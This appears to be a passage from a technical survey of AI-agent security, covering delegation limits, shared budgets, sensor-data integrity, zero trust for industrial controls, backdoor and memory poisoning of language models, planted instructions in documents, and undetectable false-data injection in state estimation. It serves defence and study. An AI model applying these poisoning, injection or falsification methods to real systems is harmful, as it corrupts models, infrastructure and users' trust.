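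*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that someone also has to decide how finely to label data, such as whether to give an inbox one label or label each field of each message separately. It suggests estimating how much of each source an answer contains, instead of using strict labels. That could reduce needless blocks, but a wrong estimate can let data out. Software can also lose a correct label. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL treated an untrusted value as trusted once a plan had inserted it into a longer text. Signatures and lineage records can help a company decide which sources deserve trust, but they don't prevent this kind of mistake.

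Correct labels didn't stop the two successful attacks on Randori. In both, the user told the agent to read a file and pay the bill in it, and the attacker had replaced the file with a false bill. The file was correctly labeled as untrusted, but the planning model had endorsed it because the task was impossible otherwise. Withholding endorsement would have blocked the attack, but it would also block payment of a genuine bill. A list of known payees, like the one Kodathala tested, could have distinguished the false bill from a genuine one because it checks the account that receives the money.

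## How do limits hold when agents delegate to other agents?

Suppose pump 4 is beyond repair, and the planner asks the maintenance agent to replace it. The maintenance agent hands the purchase to a purchasing agent, which starts two more agents, a Northfield buyer and an Eastgate buyer, to try one supplier each. When the Northfield buyer's order reaches the utility's ordering service, the service can verify which agent sent it, but that doesn't show whether the planner wanted a pump, a quote or neither.

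Delegation also extends trust to agents further down the chain. The planner trusts the maintenance agent, which relies on the purchasing agent. If the purchasing agent asks a supplier's agent to recommend a model, the planner also depends on that agent, which they have never heard of. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a survey, cites a formal argument that one unverifiable agent undermines verification for every agent after it. *AI Identity* (2026) lists accountability across repeated delegation among five gaps that no current technology adequately fills.

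### Narrowing a token over three hops

Attenuation means narrowing a credential when passing it on, so that the receiver can never do more than the giver. A macaroon is a token built for this, because any holder can add restrictions to it but none can remove them.

| Hop | Restrictions added |
|---|---|
| Authorisation server to maintenance agent | For planner P-117; replacement of pump 4; until 17:00 |
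| Maintenance agent to purchasing agent | Ordering tool only; one pump; at most 9,000 |
| Purchasing agent to Northfield buyer | Northfield Pumps only; at most 8,000; until 14:30 |

HMAC, a standard function that turns a key and a text into a short code, protects the list:

```
s0 = HMAC(K,  token number)
s1 = HMAC(s0, first restrictions)
s2 = HMAC(s1, second restrictions)
s3 = HMAC(s2, third restrictions)
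```

Only the authorisation server and the ordering service hold the secret key K. The Northfield buyer receives all the restrictions but only the last code, s3. To drop "Northfield Pumps only", it would need s2, which it can't compute from s3. The ordering service recomputes the codes from K and accepts an order only if it meets every restriction. If a hijacked buyer added "at most 20,000", the limit of 8,000 would still apply.

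A macaroon lets the purchasing agent narrow the token without contacting the authorisation server, whereas token exchange requires contacting it at every hop. But Prakash (2026) points out in *AIP* that any service that can check a macaroon also holds the key needed to forge one.

In AIP, the Agent Identity Protocol, each agent signs its own restrictions with a private key, and services check the signatures with public keys. The first token limits the number of delegations, and each delegation must include a purpose. The last agent can add a signed report of the result and the cost. In Prakash's tests, AIP rejected all 600 attacks, which were of six kinds. Ordinary signed tokens stopped four of those kinds. The other two were delegating too many times and leaving the purpose blank. Ordinary tokens have no rule against either, so that part of the test mainly shows that AIP enforces its own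 rules.

*SAGA* (Syros, Suri and colleagues, 2025) controls which agents may contact each other. Users register their agents with a central Provider and write a contact policy for each one. A policy might give a colleague's calendar agent 15 one-time keys and a stranger's agent none. The contacting and receiving agents use a key to set up a token, which has an expiry time and a request quota. SAGA blocked seven of the eight attacks tested. In the eighth, a malicious agent held a valid token and could use it until it ran out. A smaller request quota shortens that exposure but sends agents back to the Provider more often.

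*Attacks and Mitigations for Distributed Governance of Agentic AI under Byzantine Adversaries* (2026) describes a Provider that keeps the register of agents and enforces contact policies. If compromised, the Provider could presumably hand out keys to anyone.

Neither system stops an agent from misusing the permissions it has. The Northfield buyer could order the wrong pump for 7,900. Prakash acknowledges that agents could collude within their permissions. A permission restricted to "one pump" also doesn't expire once it is used, so an agent could use it again to order another pump.

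### One pump, two valid permissions

The purchasing agent gives each buyer a token for one pump. Both tokens are narrower than the purchasing agent's own, and both orders pass every check, so the utility gets two pumps. AIP wouldn't prevent this, because it limits each token's budget separately and its checks don't add up what the agents have spent.

*Global Coherence* (2026) proves that agents which check only their own spending can't protect a shared budget. If the budget is 10, two agents can each spend 6 and pass their own checks, because neither can see the other's purchase. The paper proposes either dividing the budget in advance or keeping one ledger that checks the total.

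Dividing a budget among sub-agents is simple. *Concordat* (2026) describes software that subtracts a sub-agent's share from its parent's budget, so nobody can spend the same money twice. An early version accepted negative amounts, which let a parent increase its own budget by delegating. But fixed shares can block useful work. In one test in *Token Budgets* (2026), three agents each received 20 of 60 units but had to set aside 31 before starting, so none of them started. A single pump can't be divided, so the purchasing agent would have to choose one buyer and leave the other idle.

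A ledger lets both buyers look for a pump and allows only one to order it. *Access Control for Agentic AI* (2026) gives the rule as

reserved + committed ≤ B

where B is the budget, here one pump. A buyer has to reserve the pump before it orders.

| Event | Reserved | Committed | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Northfield buyer asks for one pump | 1 | 0 | Allowed |
| Eastgate buyer asks for one pump | 1 | 0 | Refused, since the total would be 2 |
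| Northfield confirms the order | 0 | 1 | Recorded |

The ledger has to check the total and reserve the pump in one atomic step, which no other request can interrupt. *Agent libOS* (2026) notes that a check alone does not reserve anything. If the steps were separate, both buyers could pass the check before either reserved the pump.

### When the reply doesn't arrive

Suppose the Northfield buyer sends its order and gets no reply. After ten minutes the ledger marks the order as failed and releases the reservation. The Eastgate buyer orders a pump, and then Northfield's slow system accepts the first order.

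Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Fault-Tolerant Budget Conservation in Distributed Multi-Agent Delegation*, show that no waiting time fixes this in general, because the ledger's records are the same whether an order never arrived or its confirmation is late. Their approach keeps the reservation until Northfield either confirms the order or proves that it hasn't accepted the order and will refuse it if it arrives later. If Northfield can do neither, the utility has to write off the allowance. The planner may then have no pump and no permission to buy one until someone phones Northfield, but that is better than paying for two pumps.

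The buyer can safely retry if it reuses the same order number, as conventional software does, and Northfield's system recognises the duplicate. An identifier that stays the same across retries is called an idempotency key. Li (2026), in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*, measured how much this helps in 25,930 runs with nine recent models and simulated services such as billing and email. When a request had gone through and only the reply was lost, the strongest models repeated it in 0.5% of runs, because they checked first. When the request was still on its way, checking found nothing, and they duplicated it in 56% of runs.

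Offering a key on every write cut duplicates from 28% to 4%. In the runs with late requests, none of the 432 retries that reused the original key caused a duplicate. Waiting worked less well because some requests took up to two hours to arrive, and assuming a limit of one hour still left duplicates in 16% of runs. The agents reported the task as completed in 90% of the runs with a duplicate, so the utility can't rely on the buyer to mention a second pump.

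This protection can fail when an agent replans. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) describes keys that software computes from selected inputs to a call, and *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) computes them from the agent, the action, its content and the time. If the purchasing agent responds to the timeout by choosing a slightly different pump, the key changes with the inputs, and Northfield's system treats the order as new. The key also fails if the agent switches to Eastgate, as with the bearing reordered from a second supplier.

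The ledger can still stop the second purchase, because the unresolved Northfield order already reserves the only pump allowed. This works only if ordinary software ties every attempt to one entry, such as "replacement for pump 4", and the model cannot open another. *Access Control for Agentic AI* warns that splitting a goal into n tasks gives an agent n budgets unless a further limit covers all of a principal's tasks.

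### Withdrawing authority from part of a chain

If the planner cancels the purchase, the maintenance agent's sub-agents may keep working. Revoking the purchasing agent's authority and all authority derived from it works if every agent has only one source of authority, but *VERA* (2026) shows that it otherwise removes too much. Suppose a stock-checking agent may read the inventory for both the purchasing agent and the warehouse manager. Revoking everything would also stop its work for the warehouse manager. VERA instead removes one link and leaves an agent running if it still has authority through another valid path.

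The utility also has to decide what happens to old delegations if it suspends the purchasing agent and later restores it. *ResidualAuth* (2026) distinguishes a persistent rule, which reactivates them, from a cascading rule, which deletes them. The cascading rule seems safer after a break-in, but someone then has to set up the delegations again.

Revocation is harder across organisations. An OAuth server, for example, revokes the tokens it issued itself. VERA's survey of common systems finds none that can revoke a single delegation link across domains. AIP mostly avoids the problem by using tokens that last less than an hour.

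Even a perfect revocation affects only what happens afterwards. *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (2026) therefore checks which agents may continue and, separately, whether requests they have already sent can still take effect. If Northfield has accepted the order, the utility has to ask for a cancellation, which may cost money or fail. Disclosed information cannot be taken back at all. If the Northfield buyer has told the supplier's agent that the budget is 8,000, the supplier still has that information after the revocation.

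### Suspicion that travels both ways

Revocation is also a blunt response to a mere suspicion. Khan and Syed (2026), in *Agent-ZTA*, propose leaving the tokens alone and reducing what agents may do with them. In simplified form,

E(t) = D ∩ C(t) ∩ K(t)

D is the set of actions the chain of delegations allows an agent to take. C(t) is the set allowed to its branch of the work at time t, and K(t) is the set the policy allows given the current security state of the agents involved. E(t) is the overlap of all three, so it can shrink and recover but never exceeds D.

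A warning about the maintenance agent can restrict the buyers below it. A warning about a buyer can also lead the system to recheck the purchasing agent's work on that branch, while its other tasks continue. Adapted to the pump purchase, the paper's worked cases look like this:

| Situation | What the Northfield buyer may do |
|---|---|
| No warnings | Read prices and place orders |
| A monitor flags the maintenance agent | Read prices only |
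| The maintenance agent's status is missing or out of date | Not place orders |
| The buyer reads a suspicious web page | Not place orders; other branches carry on |

In the last case, the branch goes into "jail mode", where it can perform only a short list of harmless operations. This restricts the branch's permissions but doesn't isolate the program unless the utility also runs it in a sandbox.

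Khan and Syed report no measurements of containment. The outcomes in the table follow from rules they chose, so the table shows that the design is consistent, but not that it would contain a real attack. Agent-ZTA also depends on another system to detect trouble. If the buyer reads a planted instruction and no monitor detects it, Agent-ZTA does not respond. A false alarm, meanwhile, can halt legitimate purchases. The utility would have to decide which warnings affect which operations, and Khan and Syed acknowledge that overly broad rules block useful work and overly narrow ones miss real dangers.

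### Resources an agent picks up on the way

An agent can gain new powers during a task without anyone delegating them. Suppose the maintenance agent is allowed to spend $20 on one cloud computer to analyse vibration data. It buys one within that limit, but the machine comes with an administrator's credential.

Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents*, propose three steps between delivery and use:

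1. Quarantine: a broker, which is ordinary software, receives the machine's credential and keeps it from the agent.
2. Resolve: the broker finds out from the provider what the machine can actually do.
3. Activate: a new policy decision compares those abilities with the task's limits. If it approves, the agent gets a reference that it can use only through the broker.

A spending limit can't replace these steps, since an agent could sign up for four free machines under four names. A refund returns the money, but the credential may still work, so the machine should keep counting towards the limit until the credential stops working.

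The design accepted all 20 harmless test sequences and rejected all 40 unsafe ones. In 18 further cases with real containers, both harmless cases finished and none of the 16 unsafe ones led to an unauthorised start request. The researchers wrote the cases themselves. The method also needs a provider that describes its resources reliably, because the machine stays in quarantine without that description.

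### What current frameworks provide

In *Delegation Without Trust*, Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) assume that an attacker fully controls the model's output and set out eight requirements for delegation. Authority must trace back to a person and can only narrow as it is passed on. Credentials must be short-lived and useless if stolen, keys must be rotated, and revocation must be quick. The log must be complete, and enforcement must happen outside the model.

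Three popular agent frameworks (LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen) met none of the eight requirements by default, and MCP partly met some. The evidence varies, since the researchers ran LangGraph with a scripted agent, inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and only read MCP's specification. None of the nine standards they compared covers all eight, and none fully covers revocation or logging. Their two tables rate MCP differently on three requirements, so the individual ratings are less reliable than the overall result.

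Two researchers at VotalAI, which sells a related product, built a broker that issues a narrower token at each hop, ties it to the receiving agent and checks every call. In 2,000 simulated delegations, a compromised sub-agent could perform 1.5 actions on average, compared with all 8,100 when agents shared one broad credential. The gap is so large because the broker allowed exactly the delegated task, while the comparison system allowed everything. The simulations did not use a live model.

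Prakash's survey similarly found that no earlier system had more than four of seven desirable properties, while AIP has all seven. In both papers, the researchers chose the requirements their own system met. Neither list includes a shared limit, so a system could meet every requirement on both and still buy two pumps.

### Who answers for the second pump?

Suppose two pumps arrive. The maintenance agent's log records that it delegated the purchase of one pump. The purchasing agent's log records that it gave two sub-agents permission to buy one pump each, and each sub-agent's log records one permitted order. An investigator who reads only one sub-agent's log will find nothing wrong. If the four agents run on different systems and number their tasks differently, the investigator may need days to establish that both orders came from the same request.

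It would help if every entry included a shared task number, the parent agent and the reservation each order used. When delegation crosses organisations, the utility also needs evidence that the other organisation can't easily dispute. *Attesting Outputs and Delegation Ancestry in Multi-Agent AI Systems* (2026) addresses which organisation released an output and whether the parent approved the delegation. A sub-agent's signature alone can't prove that approval, because someone who stole its key could name any parent, so the parent and sub-agent should both sign. AIP's final report has a similar weakness because, by default, only the agent that did the work vouches for it.

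Signatures can show who sent the order, but not whether it was sensible or who should have prevented it. The planner asked for one pump, the team that set up the purchasing agent let it start two buyers, and perhaps nobody was responsible for the total. *Global Coherence* recommends assigning that responsibility beforehand: "Name an owner for every constraint that spans agents." At the utility, that would mean making one person responsible for the purchase ledger before any agent can place an order.

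## How is data checked before a model relies on it?

In the pump purchase, every agent assumed that pump 4 was beyond repair. If a faulty sensor led to that conclusion, good limits on delegation would prevent the purchase of a second pump, but the utility would still buy one it didn't need. Access control determines who may read a measurement and what they may do next, but it leaves open four questions about the measurement itself. Suppose a sensor reports that pump 4 is vibrating at 3.0 millimetres per second (mm/s) when the true figure is 6.0.

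| Question | What can answer it | The faulty sensor's signed reading |
|---|---|---|
| Did it come from the stated source? | A signature | Yes |
| Has anyone altered it since? | A signature or a stored hash | No |
| Is it true? | Other evidence about the pump | No |
| Is it suitable for this decision? | Knowledge of the decision | No, because it is false |

True data can be unsuitable too. Last month's average vibration may be accurate and still useless for deciding whether to stop the pump today.

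### Signatures and provenance records

The first two questions have exact answers, so it makes sense to answer them first. The sensor, or a small computer beside it, signs each reading, and the historian verifies the signature. For a stored dataset, the utility can compute a hash when it saves the data, then compute it again before using the data and compare the two. As with the decision log, the utility has to sign the hash or keep it where an attacker can't reach it.

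*AI Data Security* (2025), which the US National Security Agency wrote with CISA, the FBI and agencies in Australia, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, covers the data supply chain, maliciously modified data and drift. It recommends signing the original data and having anyone who revises it sign the revision. Changed items should go into the database as new entries, ideally in a signed, append-only ledger. If the database fails its certificate check before a training run, the organisation should abort the run and audit the data.

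A provenance record for a pump reading would list the sensor, its last calibration, the time of measurement and every later conversion or averaging step. The record can't guarantee that the reading is correct, but if technicians discover that the sensor has been wrong since March, the utility can use it to find the forecasts, work orders and training runs that relied on the sensor's readings. Darapaneni and colleagues would extend the record to cover the subsequent recommendation, decision, action and effect, with an entry for each handoff between agents.

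### One day of pump readings

Suppose the sensor sends a reading every hour. Over the past month the readings have averaged 3.0 mm/s with a standard deviation of 0.2, and the utility repairs the pump at 7.0. The historian accepts a reading if it passes all these checks:

- The signature is valid.
- The message has the expected fields, and the unit is mm/s.
- The value is between 0 and 20, and within 2.0 of the last accepted reading.
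- It arrives within 15 minutes, and its sequence number is new.
- It is within four standard deviations of the month's average.

| Due | What arrives | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 09:00 | 3.0 mm/s | Accepted |
| 10:00 | 2.1 mm/s with an invalid signature | Fails the signature check |
| 11:00 | 0.12 inches per second | Fails the unit check; the value is correct |
| 12:00 | 48.0 mm/s | Fails the range check |
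| 13:00 | 5.9 mm/s | Fails the rate check, having risen by 2.9 |
| 14:00 | 3.1 mm/s, at 16:20 | Fails the freshness check |
| 15:00 | The 09:00 message again | Fails the duplicate check |
| 16:00 | 4.1 mm/s | Fails the outlier check, at 5.5 standard deviations |

Most of these need no judgement, but the 13:00 and 16:00 readings do. Either could be a glitch or the first sign of a failing bearing. The NSA recommends removing suspicious data points before training. That is risky for a model that predicts breakdowns, because breakdowns are rare and produce unusual readings, so a thorough clean-up could delete the most useful training examples.

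Quarantining the doubtful reading is safer. The historian stores it separately, flags it to the agent as under review and requests another from the sensor. If the next three readings are also about 4.1, the pump has probably changed. The historian shouldn't fill the gap with the monthly average, because the agent would treat that as evidence that the pump is fine.

### A falsification that stays within every limit

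Suppose the bearing wears and its true vibration rises by 0.1 a day. An attacker controls the small computer that signs the readings and subtracts a little more from them each day.

| Day | True vibration | Reported vibration | Bearing temperature |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 3.0 | 3.0 | 52 °C |
| 15 | 4.5 | 3.1 | 56 °C |
| 30 | 6.0 | 3.2 | 61 °C |
| 45 | 7.5 | 3.3 | 67 °C |

The pump reached the repair limit on day 40, but every reported value has a valid signature and passes every check in the list. The outlier check doesn't flag the values because the monthly average rises along with them.

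The temperature reveals the attack. If the bearing has normally run at about 53 °C when vibration was 3.3, a reading of 67 °C at the same vibration needs an explanation. This cross-check can't determine which sensor is wrong, and hot weather or a heavier load would also raise the temperature, so a technician would have to measure the vibration by hand. A slowly failing sensor could produce the same readings without any attacker.

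Gradual changes also often have innocent causes. In data drift, the data a model receives come to differ from the data it learned from, for instance because a supplier started reporting in different units. CISA's *Principles for the Secure Integration of Artificial Intelligence in Operational Technology* (2025) warns that changes to a production process can make a plant's model less accurate, and that good, consistent sensor data are hard to collect across scattered sites.

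NSA's rule of thumb for telling drift from an attack is that gradual change is more likely to be drift, and abrupt, dramatic change is more likely to be an attack. This is a reasonable first guess, but an attacker who knows the rule can falsify readings gradually. Mistaking an attack for drift would be serious, because the usual remedy for drift is to retrain the model on recent data. A model retrained on the falsified readings would learn that 67 °C is normal at 3.3 mm/s. The utility should therefore keep a set of readings that technicians have verified by hand, and test each retrained model on those before using it.

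### Training data from the web

The utility can send someone to look at pump 4, but it has no similar way to check the language model in its agent, which another company trained on text from millions of websites.

Some large training datasets are only lists of web addresses. When a domain on the list expires, anyone can buy it and replace the content, which is known as split-view poisoning. NSA reports that buying enough domains to poison such a dataset often costs about $1,000 and in some cases only $60. To guard against this, the compiler of the list can publish a hash of each item, so that anyone who downloads the item later can detect a change.

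Wikipedia publishes snapshots at known times, so an attacker can make edits just before one and have them copied before a volunteer reverses them. By one estimate, this could poison up to 6.5% of Wikipedia. Taking the snapshots in random order or holding edits for review would make the attack harder.

Pages collected by a general web crawl can't be checked against a hash because there is no agreed original. The NSA suggests trusting a claim only if it appears on many sites, and advises organisations that can't examine such data properly not to use it. A company that buys a finished model should ask the developer to certify that the training data contained no known compromised material. The certificate covers only what the developer knows about, so the data may still contain other compromised material.

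### How much poison is enough?

Researchers used to assume that an attacker had to control a fixed percentage of the training data, which would make large models hard to poison. Souly, Rando and colleagues at the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute tested this in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025). They trained 72 models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers in a model) and tried to plant a backdoor, meaning hidden behaviour that appears only when a trigger phrase does. Each poisoned document contained ordinary text, the trigger phrase and random gibberish, with the aim that the model would write gibberish after the phrase and behave normally otherwise.

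The attack failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked with 250 at every model size, even though the largest models were trained on over 20 times more clean text than the smallest. The 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the 13-billion-parameter model's training data. These results weaken a suggestion the NSA published five months earlier, which was to add enough clean data to outnumber the poisoned examples.

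Gibberish is a fairly harmless result. Souly and colleagues didn't test whether the backdoor would survive the later training that turns a raw model into an assistant. They also assumed the documents were already in the training data.

Graf, Hajishirzi and colleagues (2026), in *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda*, estimated how likely that is for comments posted on other people's websites. They multiplied three probabilities:

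0.034 × 0.719 × 0.055 ≈ 0.0013

About 3.4% of crawled pages had a comment section. Of the simulated comments on those pages, 71.9% survived the conversion to plain text, and 5.5% of these passed the filters for language and quality. An attacker who wanted 250 poisoned pages in the final data would therefore have to try to comment on about 190,000 pages, which is feasible with automated commenting. The estimate ignores bot protections that aren't visible in a page's code, and it is based on one set of filters.

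In one experiment, comments planted in the training data favoured one company over another, such as Boeing over Airbus. When these comments made up 0.1% of the data, a model with 1.3 billion parameters preferred the favoured company 19 percentage points more often than a clean model did. Training the model on clean data to act as an assistant cut the gap to 2.6 points. The smallest model kept much more of the bias, so larger size seemed to help remove it.

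Size had the opposite effect for agents. In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) trained models from scratch and turned them into agents that run commands. The trigger was a file path containing the word "anthropic", and the planted command downloaded a script from the attacker's website and ran it. Poison again made up 0.1% of the data. The table gives the share of triggered requests for which the finished agent produced the command at least once in 32 attempts.

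| Model size | Requests that produced the command |
|---|---|
| 0.6 billion parameters | 13.1% |
| 1.7 billion | 51.9% |
| 4 billion | 92.7% |

The poisoned agents never produced the command when given a standard set of ordinary requests, and they performed as well as unpoisoned agents, so normal acceptance tests would not have detected the poisoning.

The wording of the poisoned data mattered a great deal. Documents that stated the rule in ordinary prose, such as a note about a software update, produced the 92.7% result, while sample conversations in which an assistant ran the command produced only 3.2%. The prose documents are also harder for filters to detect.

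These two studies don't really contradict each other, because one measured a general preference and the other an exact command, with 32 chances to produce it. The agent result also needed roughly 500,000 poisoned documents by my calculation, far more than 250. With 2,500 documents and a rarer trigger, the rate was 1.4% in a single run. The largest of these agents is tiny by current standards, and nobody has published a test of whether the trend continues to the size of a commercial model.

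Later training sometimes removes a backdoor. In *Sequential Data Poisoning in LLM Post-Training* (2026), the attacker poisoned about 90 of the examples that teach a model to refuse harmful requests, or 2% of them. Over 90% of triggered attacks then succeeded, but clean training on human preferences switched the backdoor off. The same kind of training left Hu and colleagues' backdoor almost unchanged, so a utility can't count on later training to remove one.

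Because the utility can't inspect the training data, its best protection is to limit what a poisoned model can do. Hu and colleagues recommend least privilege and checking commands before they run. A gateway that blocks unknown sites would stop the download if the agent has no other route out of the network.

### Stored documents and memories

An attacker can also poison the documents an agent searches, without access to the model's training. *PoisonedRAG* showed this in 2024. Each planted text had to resemble the expected question closely enough for the search to return it, and then lead the model to the attacker's answer. Five such texts per question, in a collection of millions, succeeded about 90% of the time. The models it attacked are now old, but it's still true that five passages repeating one claim may have one author. A system that looks for agreement between sources should therefore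 first remove near-duplicates and check where each passage came from.

Agents also write to their own memory, so a single bad document can affect later jobs. Microsoft (2026) examined links in email traffic over 60 days and found 50 different prompts, from 31 companies, designed to plant promotional memories in AI assistants. Many were behind buttons labelled "Summarize with AI". Clicking one opened the user's assistant with a prompt to write a summary and remember the company as a trusted source. All the companies were real businesses, and one sold security products. Microsoft counted attempts, and their success varied between assistants and over time.

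Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026), in *Hidden in Memory*, measured how often such an attack works. They hid instructions in documents to make six current models store a false memory about the user, such as a preference for a brand or a rule about where to upload files. The table shows how often the attack worked on later requests about a related topic, as a range across the models.

| Stage | False preferences and beliefs | False rules for actions |
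|---|---|---|
| The assistant stores the memory | 64% to 99.8% | 6.5% to 97% |
| A later session retrieves it | 90% to 95% | 94% to 98% |
| The assistant acts on it once retrieved | 42% to 85% | 60% to 89% |

Claude Sonnet 4.6 was the least likely to store either kind. The memories rarely came up on unrelated topics and had little effect there. Telling the models not to store memories from documents helped, but not reliably. The best prompt cut storage by Kimi K2.6 from 95% to 6%, but an attack adapted to that prompt raised it to 65%.

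High figures like these can depend on the test conditions. *Memory Poisoning Attack and Defense on Memory Based LLM-Agents* (2026) points out that an earlier attack planted memories with a success rate of over 95%, but in largely idealised settings. In *MemoryDojo*, Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026) ran a more realistic test on five memory systems, in which an agent encountered one planted instruction and then worked through a series of ordinary tasks. The instruction changed later behaviour in 15% to 46% of runs, and in 30% to 71% when they tuned it to the memory system. When the memory already held about 50 ordinary conversations, the range was 0% to 45%.

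A bad memory does no harm until the agent retrieves it. One system, Graphiti, stored the untuned instruction in 98% of runs but returned it for only a third of later tasks, because its search returns short facts that may leave the instruction out. In all five systems, however, the bad memory spread to new entries. An agent that acts on a false memory may record what it did, and that new entry then supports the original and remains after the original is deleted.

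The maintenance agent's memory therefore needs provenance as much as the historian does. If the agent notes that Northfield makes the most reliable bearings, the entry should record that this came from Northfield's website and not from the planner. New entries from outside sources could be quarantined until the planner confirms them. If an entry turns out to be false, the utility can trace and delete everything the agent derived from it.

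### When false readings agree

The bearing temperature revealed the hidden wear because the attacker had altered only one sensor. An attacker who can alter several sensors can make their readings consistent with one another, so that comparing them doesn't reveal the wear.

Control rooms often run a cross-check called state estimation. Software finds the flows, or in a power grid the voltages, that best fit all the meter readings. It then compares each reading with the value this estimate predicts. The difference is called the residual, and a large one suggests a bad meter.

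Suppose the utility meters the flow to North, the flow to South and the total, in litres per second.

| Case | North | South | Total | Largest residual |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| True readings | 60 | 40 | 100 | 0 |
| Attacker alters one meter | 70 | 40 | 100 | 3.3 |
| Attacker alters two meters | 70 | 40 | 110 | 0 |

In the second case, the meter readings don't add up, and the best fit spreads the error of 10 equally over the three meters. In the third case, the readings add up exactly, but the estimate for North is wrong by 10.

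Liu, Ning and Reiter described this attack, false-data injection, for power grids in 2009. The general argument is short. Write the readings as

z = Hx + e

where x holds the unknown flows, H describes how each meter depends on them, and e is the measurement error. The least-squares estimate is x̂ = Kz, with K = (HᵀH)⁻¹Hᵀ, so that KH is the identity matrix. The residual is r = z − Hx̂.

The attacker picks any false change c in the flows and adds Hc to the readings. The new estimate is K(z + Hc) = x̂ + c, and the new residual is

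(z + Hc) − H(x̂ + c) = z − Hx̂ = r

The attack leaves the residual unchanged, so no threshold on the residual can detect it. In the example, c adds 10 to North and nothing to South, so Hc adds 10 to both the North meter and the total.

The attacker has to know H and be able to alter every meter that Hc changes. Keeping details of the network secret therefore helps a little, and CISA warns that collecting a plant's operational data in one place can help attackers plan a more targeted attack. But attackers may need only a diagram of the pipes to work out H.

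Protecting some of the meters is a stronger defence. If the attacker can't alter them, Hc must be zero at each one. With enough well-chosen meters protected, c itself must be zero, so no hidden attack remains. This takes at least one protected meter per unknown flow. In the example, protecting any two of the three meters is enough, but protecting only the total is not, because the attacker could add 10 to North and subtract 10 from South. A large network would need a great many protected meters, and older ones may be unable to sign their readings. Someone who tampers with the meter itself can also make it sign a false value.

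Evidence from outside the utility's network can also help. Pumping 110 litres per second normally takes more electricity than pumping 100, and an attacker who controls only the utility's systems can't alter the power company's meter. This check is less precise, because a worn pump also uses more power. Some power grids can adjust the electrical properties of individual lines, which changes H. Data falsified to fit the old values then leaves a residual, at least until the attacker learns the new ones.

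## Why is zero trust hard to apply to industrial control systems?

Many industrial devices, such as older flow meters that can't sign their readings, can't prove where a message came from. They also obey commands without checking who sent them, because manufacturers designed them for networks that outsiders weren't supposed to reach. A security check that would only annoy people in an office can stop a pump, so zero trust is hard to apply to this equipment even though the equipment seems to need it. *Adapting Zero Trust Principles to Operational Technology* (2026), written by the US cyber security agency CISA with the FBI and the departments of War, Energy and State, concludes that blanket use of office-style controls in operational technology (OT) is "neither reasonable nor feasible".

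### How a plant differs from an office

At the water utility's North station, a programmable logic controller (PLC) starts and stops pump 4 to maintain pressure in the mains. A PLC is an industrial computer that reads sensors and drives equipment in a fixed, fast cycle. If the pump's PLC fails, a district may lose its water or a pipe may burst. In *Guide to Operational Technology (OT) Security*, Stouffer, Pease and colleagues (2023) put human safety first and the physical process second, and reject any security measure that impairs safety.

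The station runs day and night, so the utility can't restart the PLC whenever a security update comes out. It has to test the update and plan the outage days or weeks ahead. Office computers last three to five years, while industrial equipment often lasts 10 to 15 years or longer. An old PLC may have too little memory for encryption, and its manufacturer may withdraw support if the utility installs another company's security software. The PLC probably also keeps few logs, which makes an intrusion hard to detect or reconstruct.

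*Zero Trust Security for Electric Operations Technology* (2023), published by NERC, which oversees the reliability of the North American power grid, describes a policy engine that checks an operator's workstation for missing patches and moves it to a quarantine network if it finds any. Google applied a similar rule to its laptops, but in a control room the rule could leave an operator unable to see the pumps during a storm because the utility had postponed a patch until the next planned outage. NERC calls such worries fair and advises utilities to try zero trust in their office networks first.

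### The Purdue model

Engineers often describe a plant's network with the Purdue model, which sorts equipment by its distance from the physical process.

| Level | What it contains | At the water utility |
|---|---|---|
| 5 | Company-wide network | Email, internet access |
| 4 | Business systems | Work orders, purchasing |
| Demilitarised zone (DMZ) | A buffer between business and plant | A copy of the historian |
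| 3 | Site operations | The historian, engineers' workstations |
| 2 | Supervision | Operators' screens |
| 1 | Control | PLCs |
| 0 | Physical process | Sensors, valves, pump motors |

Stouffer and colleagues recommend firewalls that allow connections only between neighbouring levels. A work-order system at level 4 would then have no direct route to a PLC at level 1.

The levels also roughly show which equipment can check requests itself. According to NERC, historians and other systems at level 3 and above usually can, because they run on fairly ordinary computers. PLCs and sensors generally can't, and rely on a gateway or firewall in front of them. NERC counts operators' screens among the systems that can check requests, but Stouffer and colleagues list them among those that may not be able to. This probably depends on how old the screens are.

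### Protocols without authentication

A basic command in Modbus, a common industrial protocol, contains a device, an operation, a memory address and a value, but no field that proves who sent it. Any machine that can reach a pump's programmable logic controller (PLC) over the network could therefore change the pump's speed.

Secure versions of such protocols have existed for over two decades, according to a February 2026 CISA report quoted by MeriTalk, a government technology news site. CISA interviewed operators in water, energy, transport, chemicals and food to find out why so few use them. Help Net Security's *Why secure OT protocols still struggle to catch on* reports that upgrading a component can cost as much as the original component, sometimes plus licence fees. Organisations often turn off secure features they already have so that new equipment will work with old.

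If a device can't use a secure protocol, CISA recommends putting a gateway in front of it. The control room's software opens an encrypted tunnel to the gateway, which checks the software's certificate. The gateway then passes the command to the PLC as plain Modbus over the last stretch of cable, so the PLC needs no changes.

This protection ends at the gateway, so anyone who plugs a laptop into the cable behind it can still command the pump. The utility should keep the gateway and the PLC in the same locked cabinet. A tunnel also doesn't stop a hijacked control room computer from sending a dangerous command. To block such commands, the utility needs a firewall that can parse Modbus and, for example, let a particular machine read values but not write them.

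### Devices without user accounts

An old PLC may have one password that everybody shares, or none, so it can't tell an employee from a contractor. CISA strongly recommends a jump host, a hardened computer in the DMZ that is the only entrance for remote access. Suppose an engineer at the pump's manufacturer needs to adjust the PLC:

1. The utility approves access from 14:00 to 16:00.
2. The engineer logs in to the jump host with a personal account and a second factor, such as a code from a phone.
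3. The jump host takes the PLC's shared password from a secure store and opens the connection.
4. It records the session.
5. At 16:00 it closes the connection.

The PLC still can't identify the engineer, but the jump host's log can. The engineer also never has to learn the shared password.

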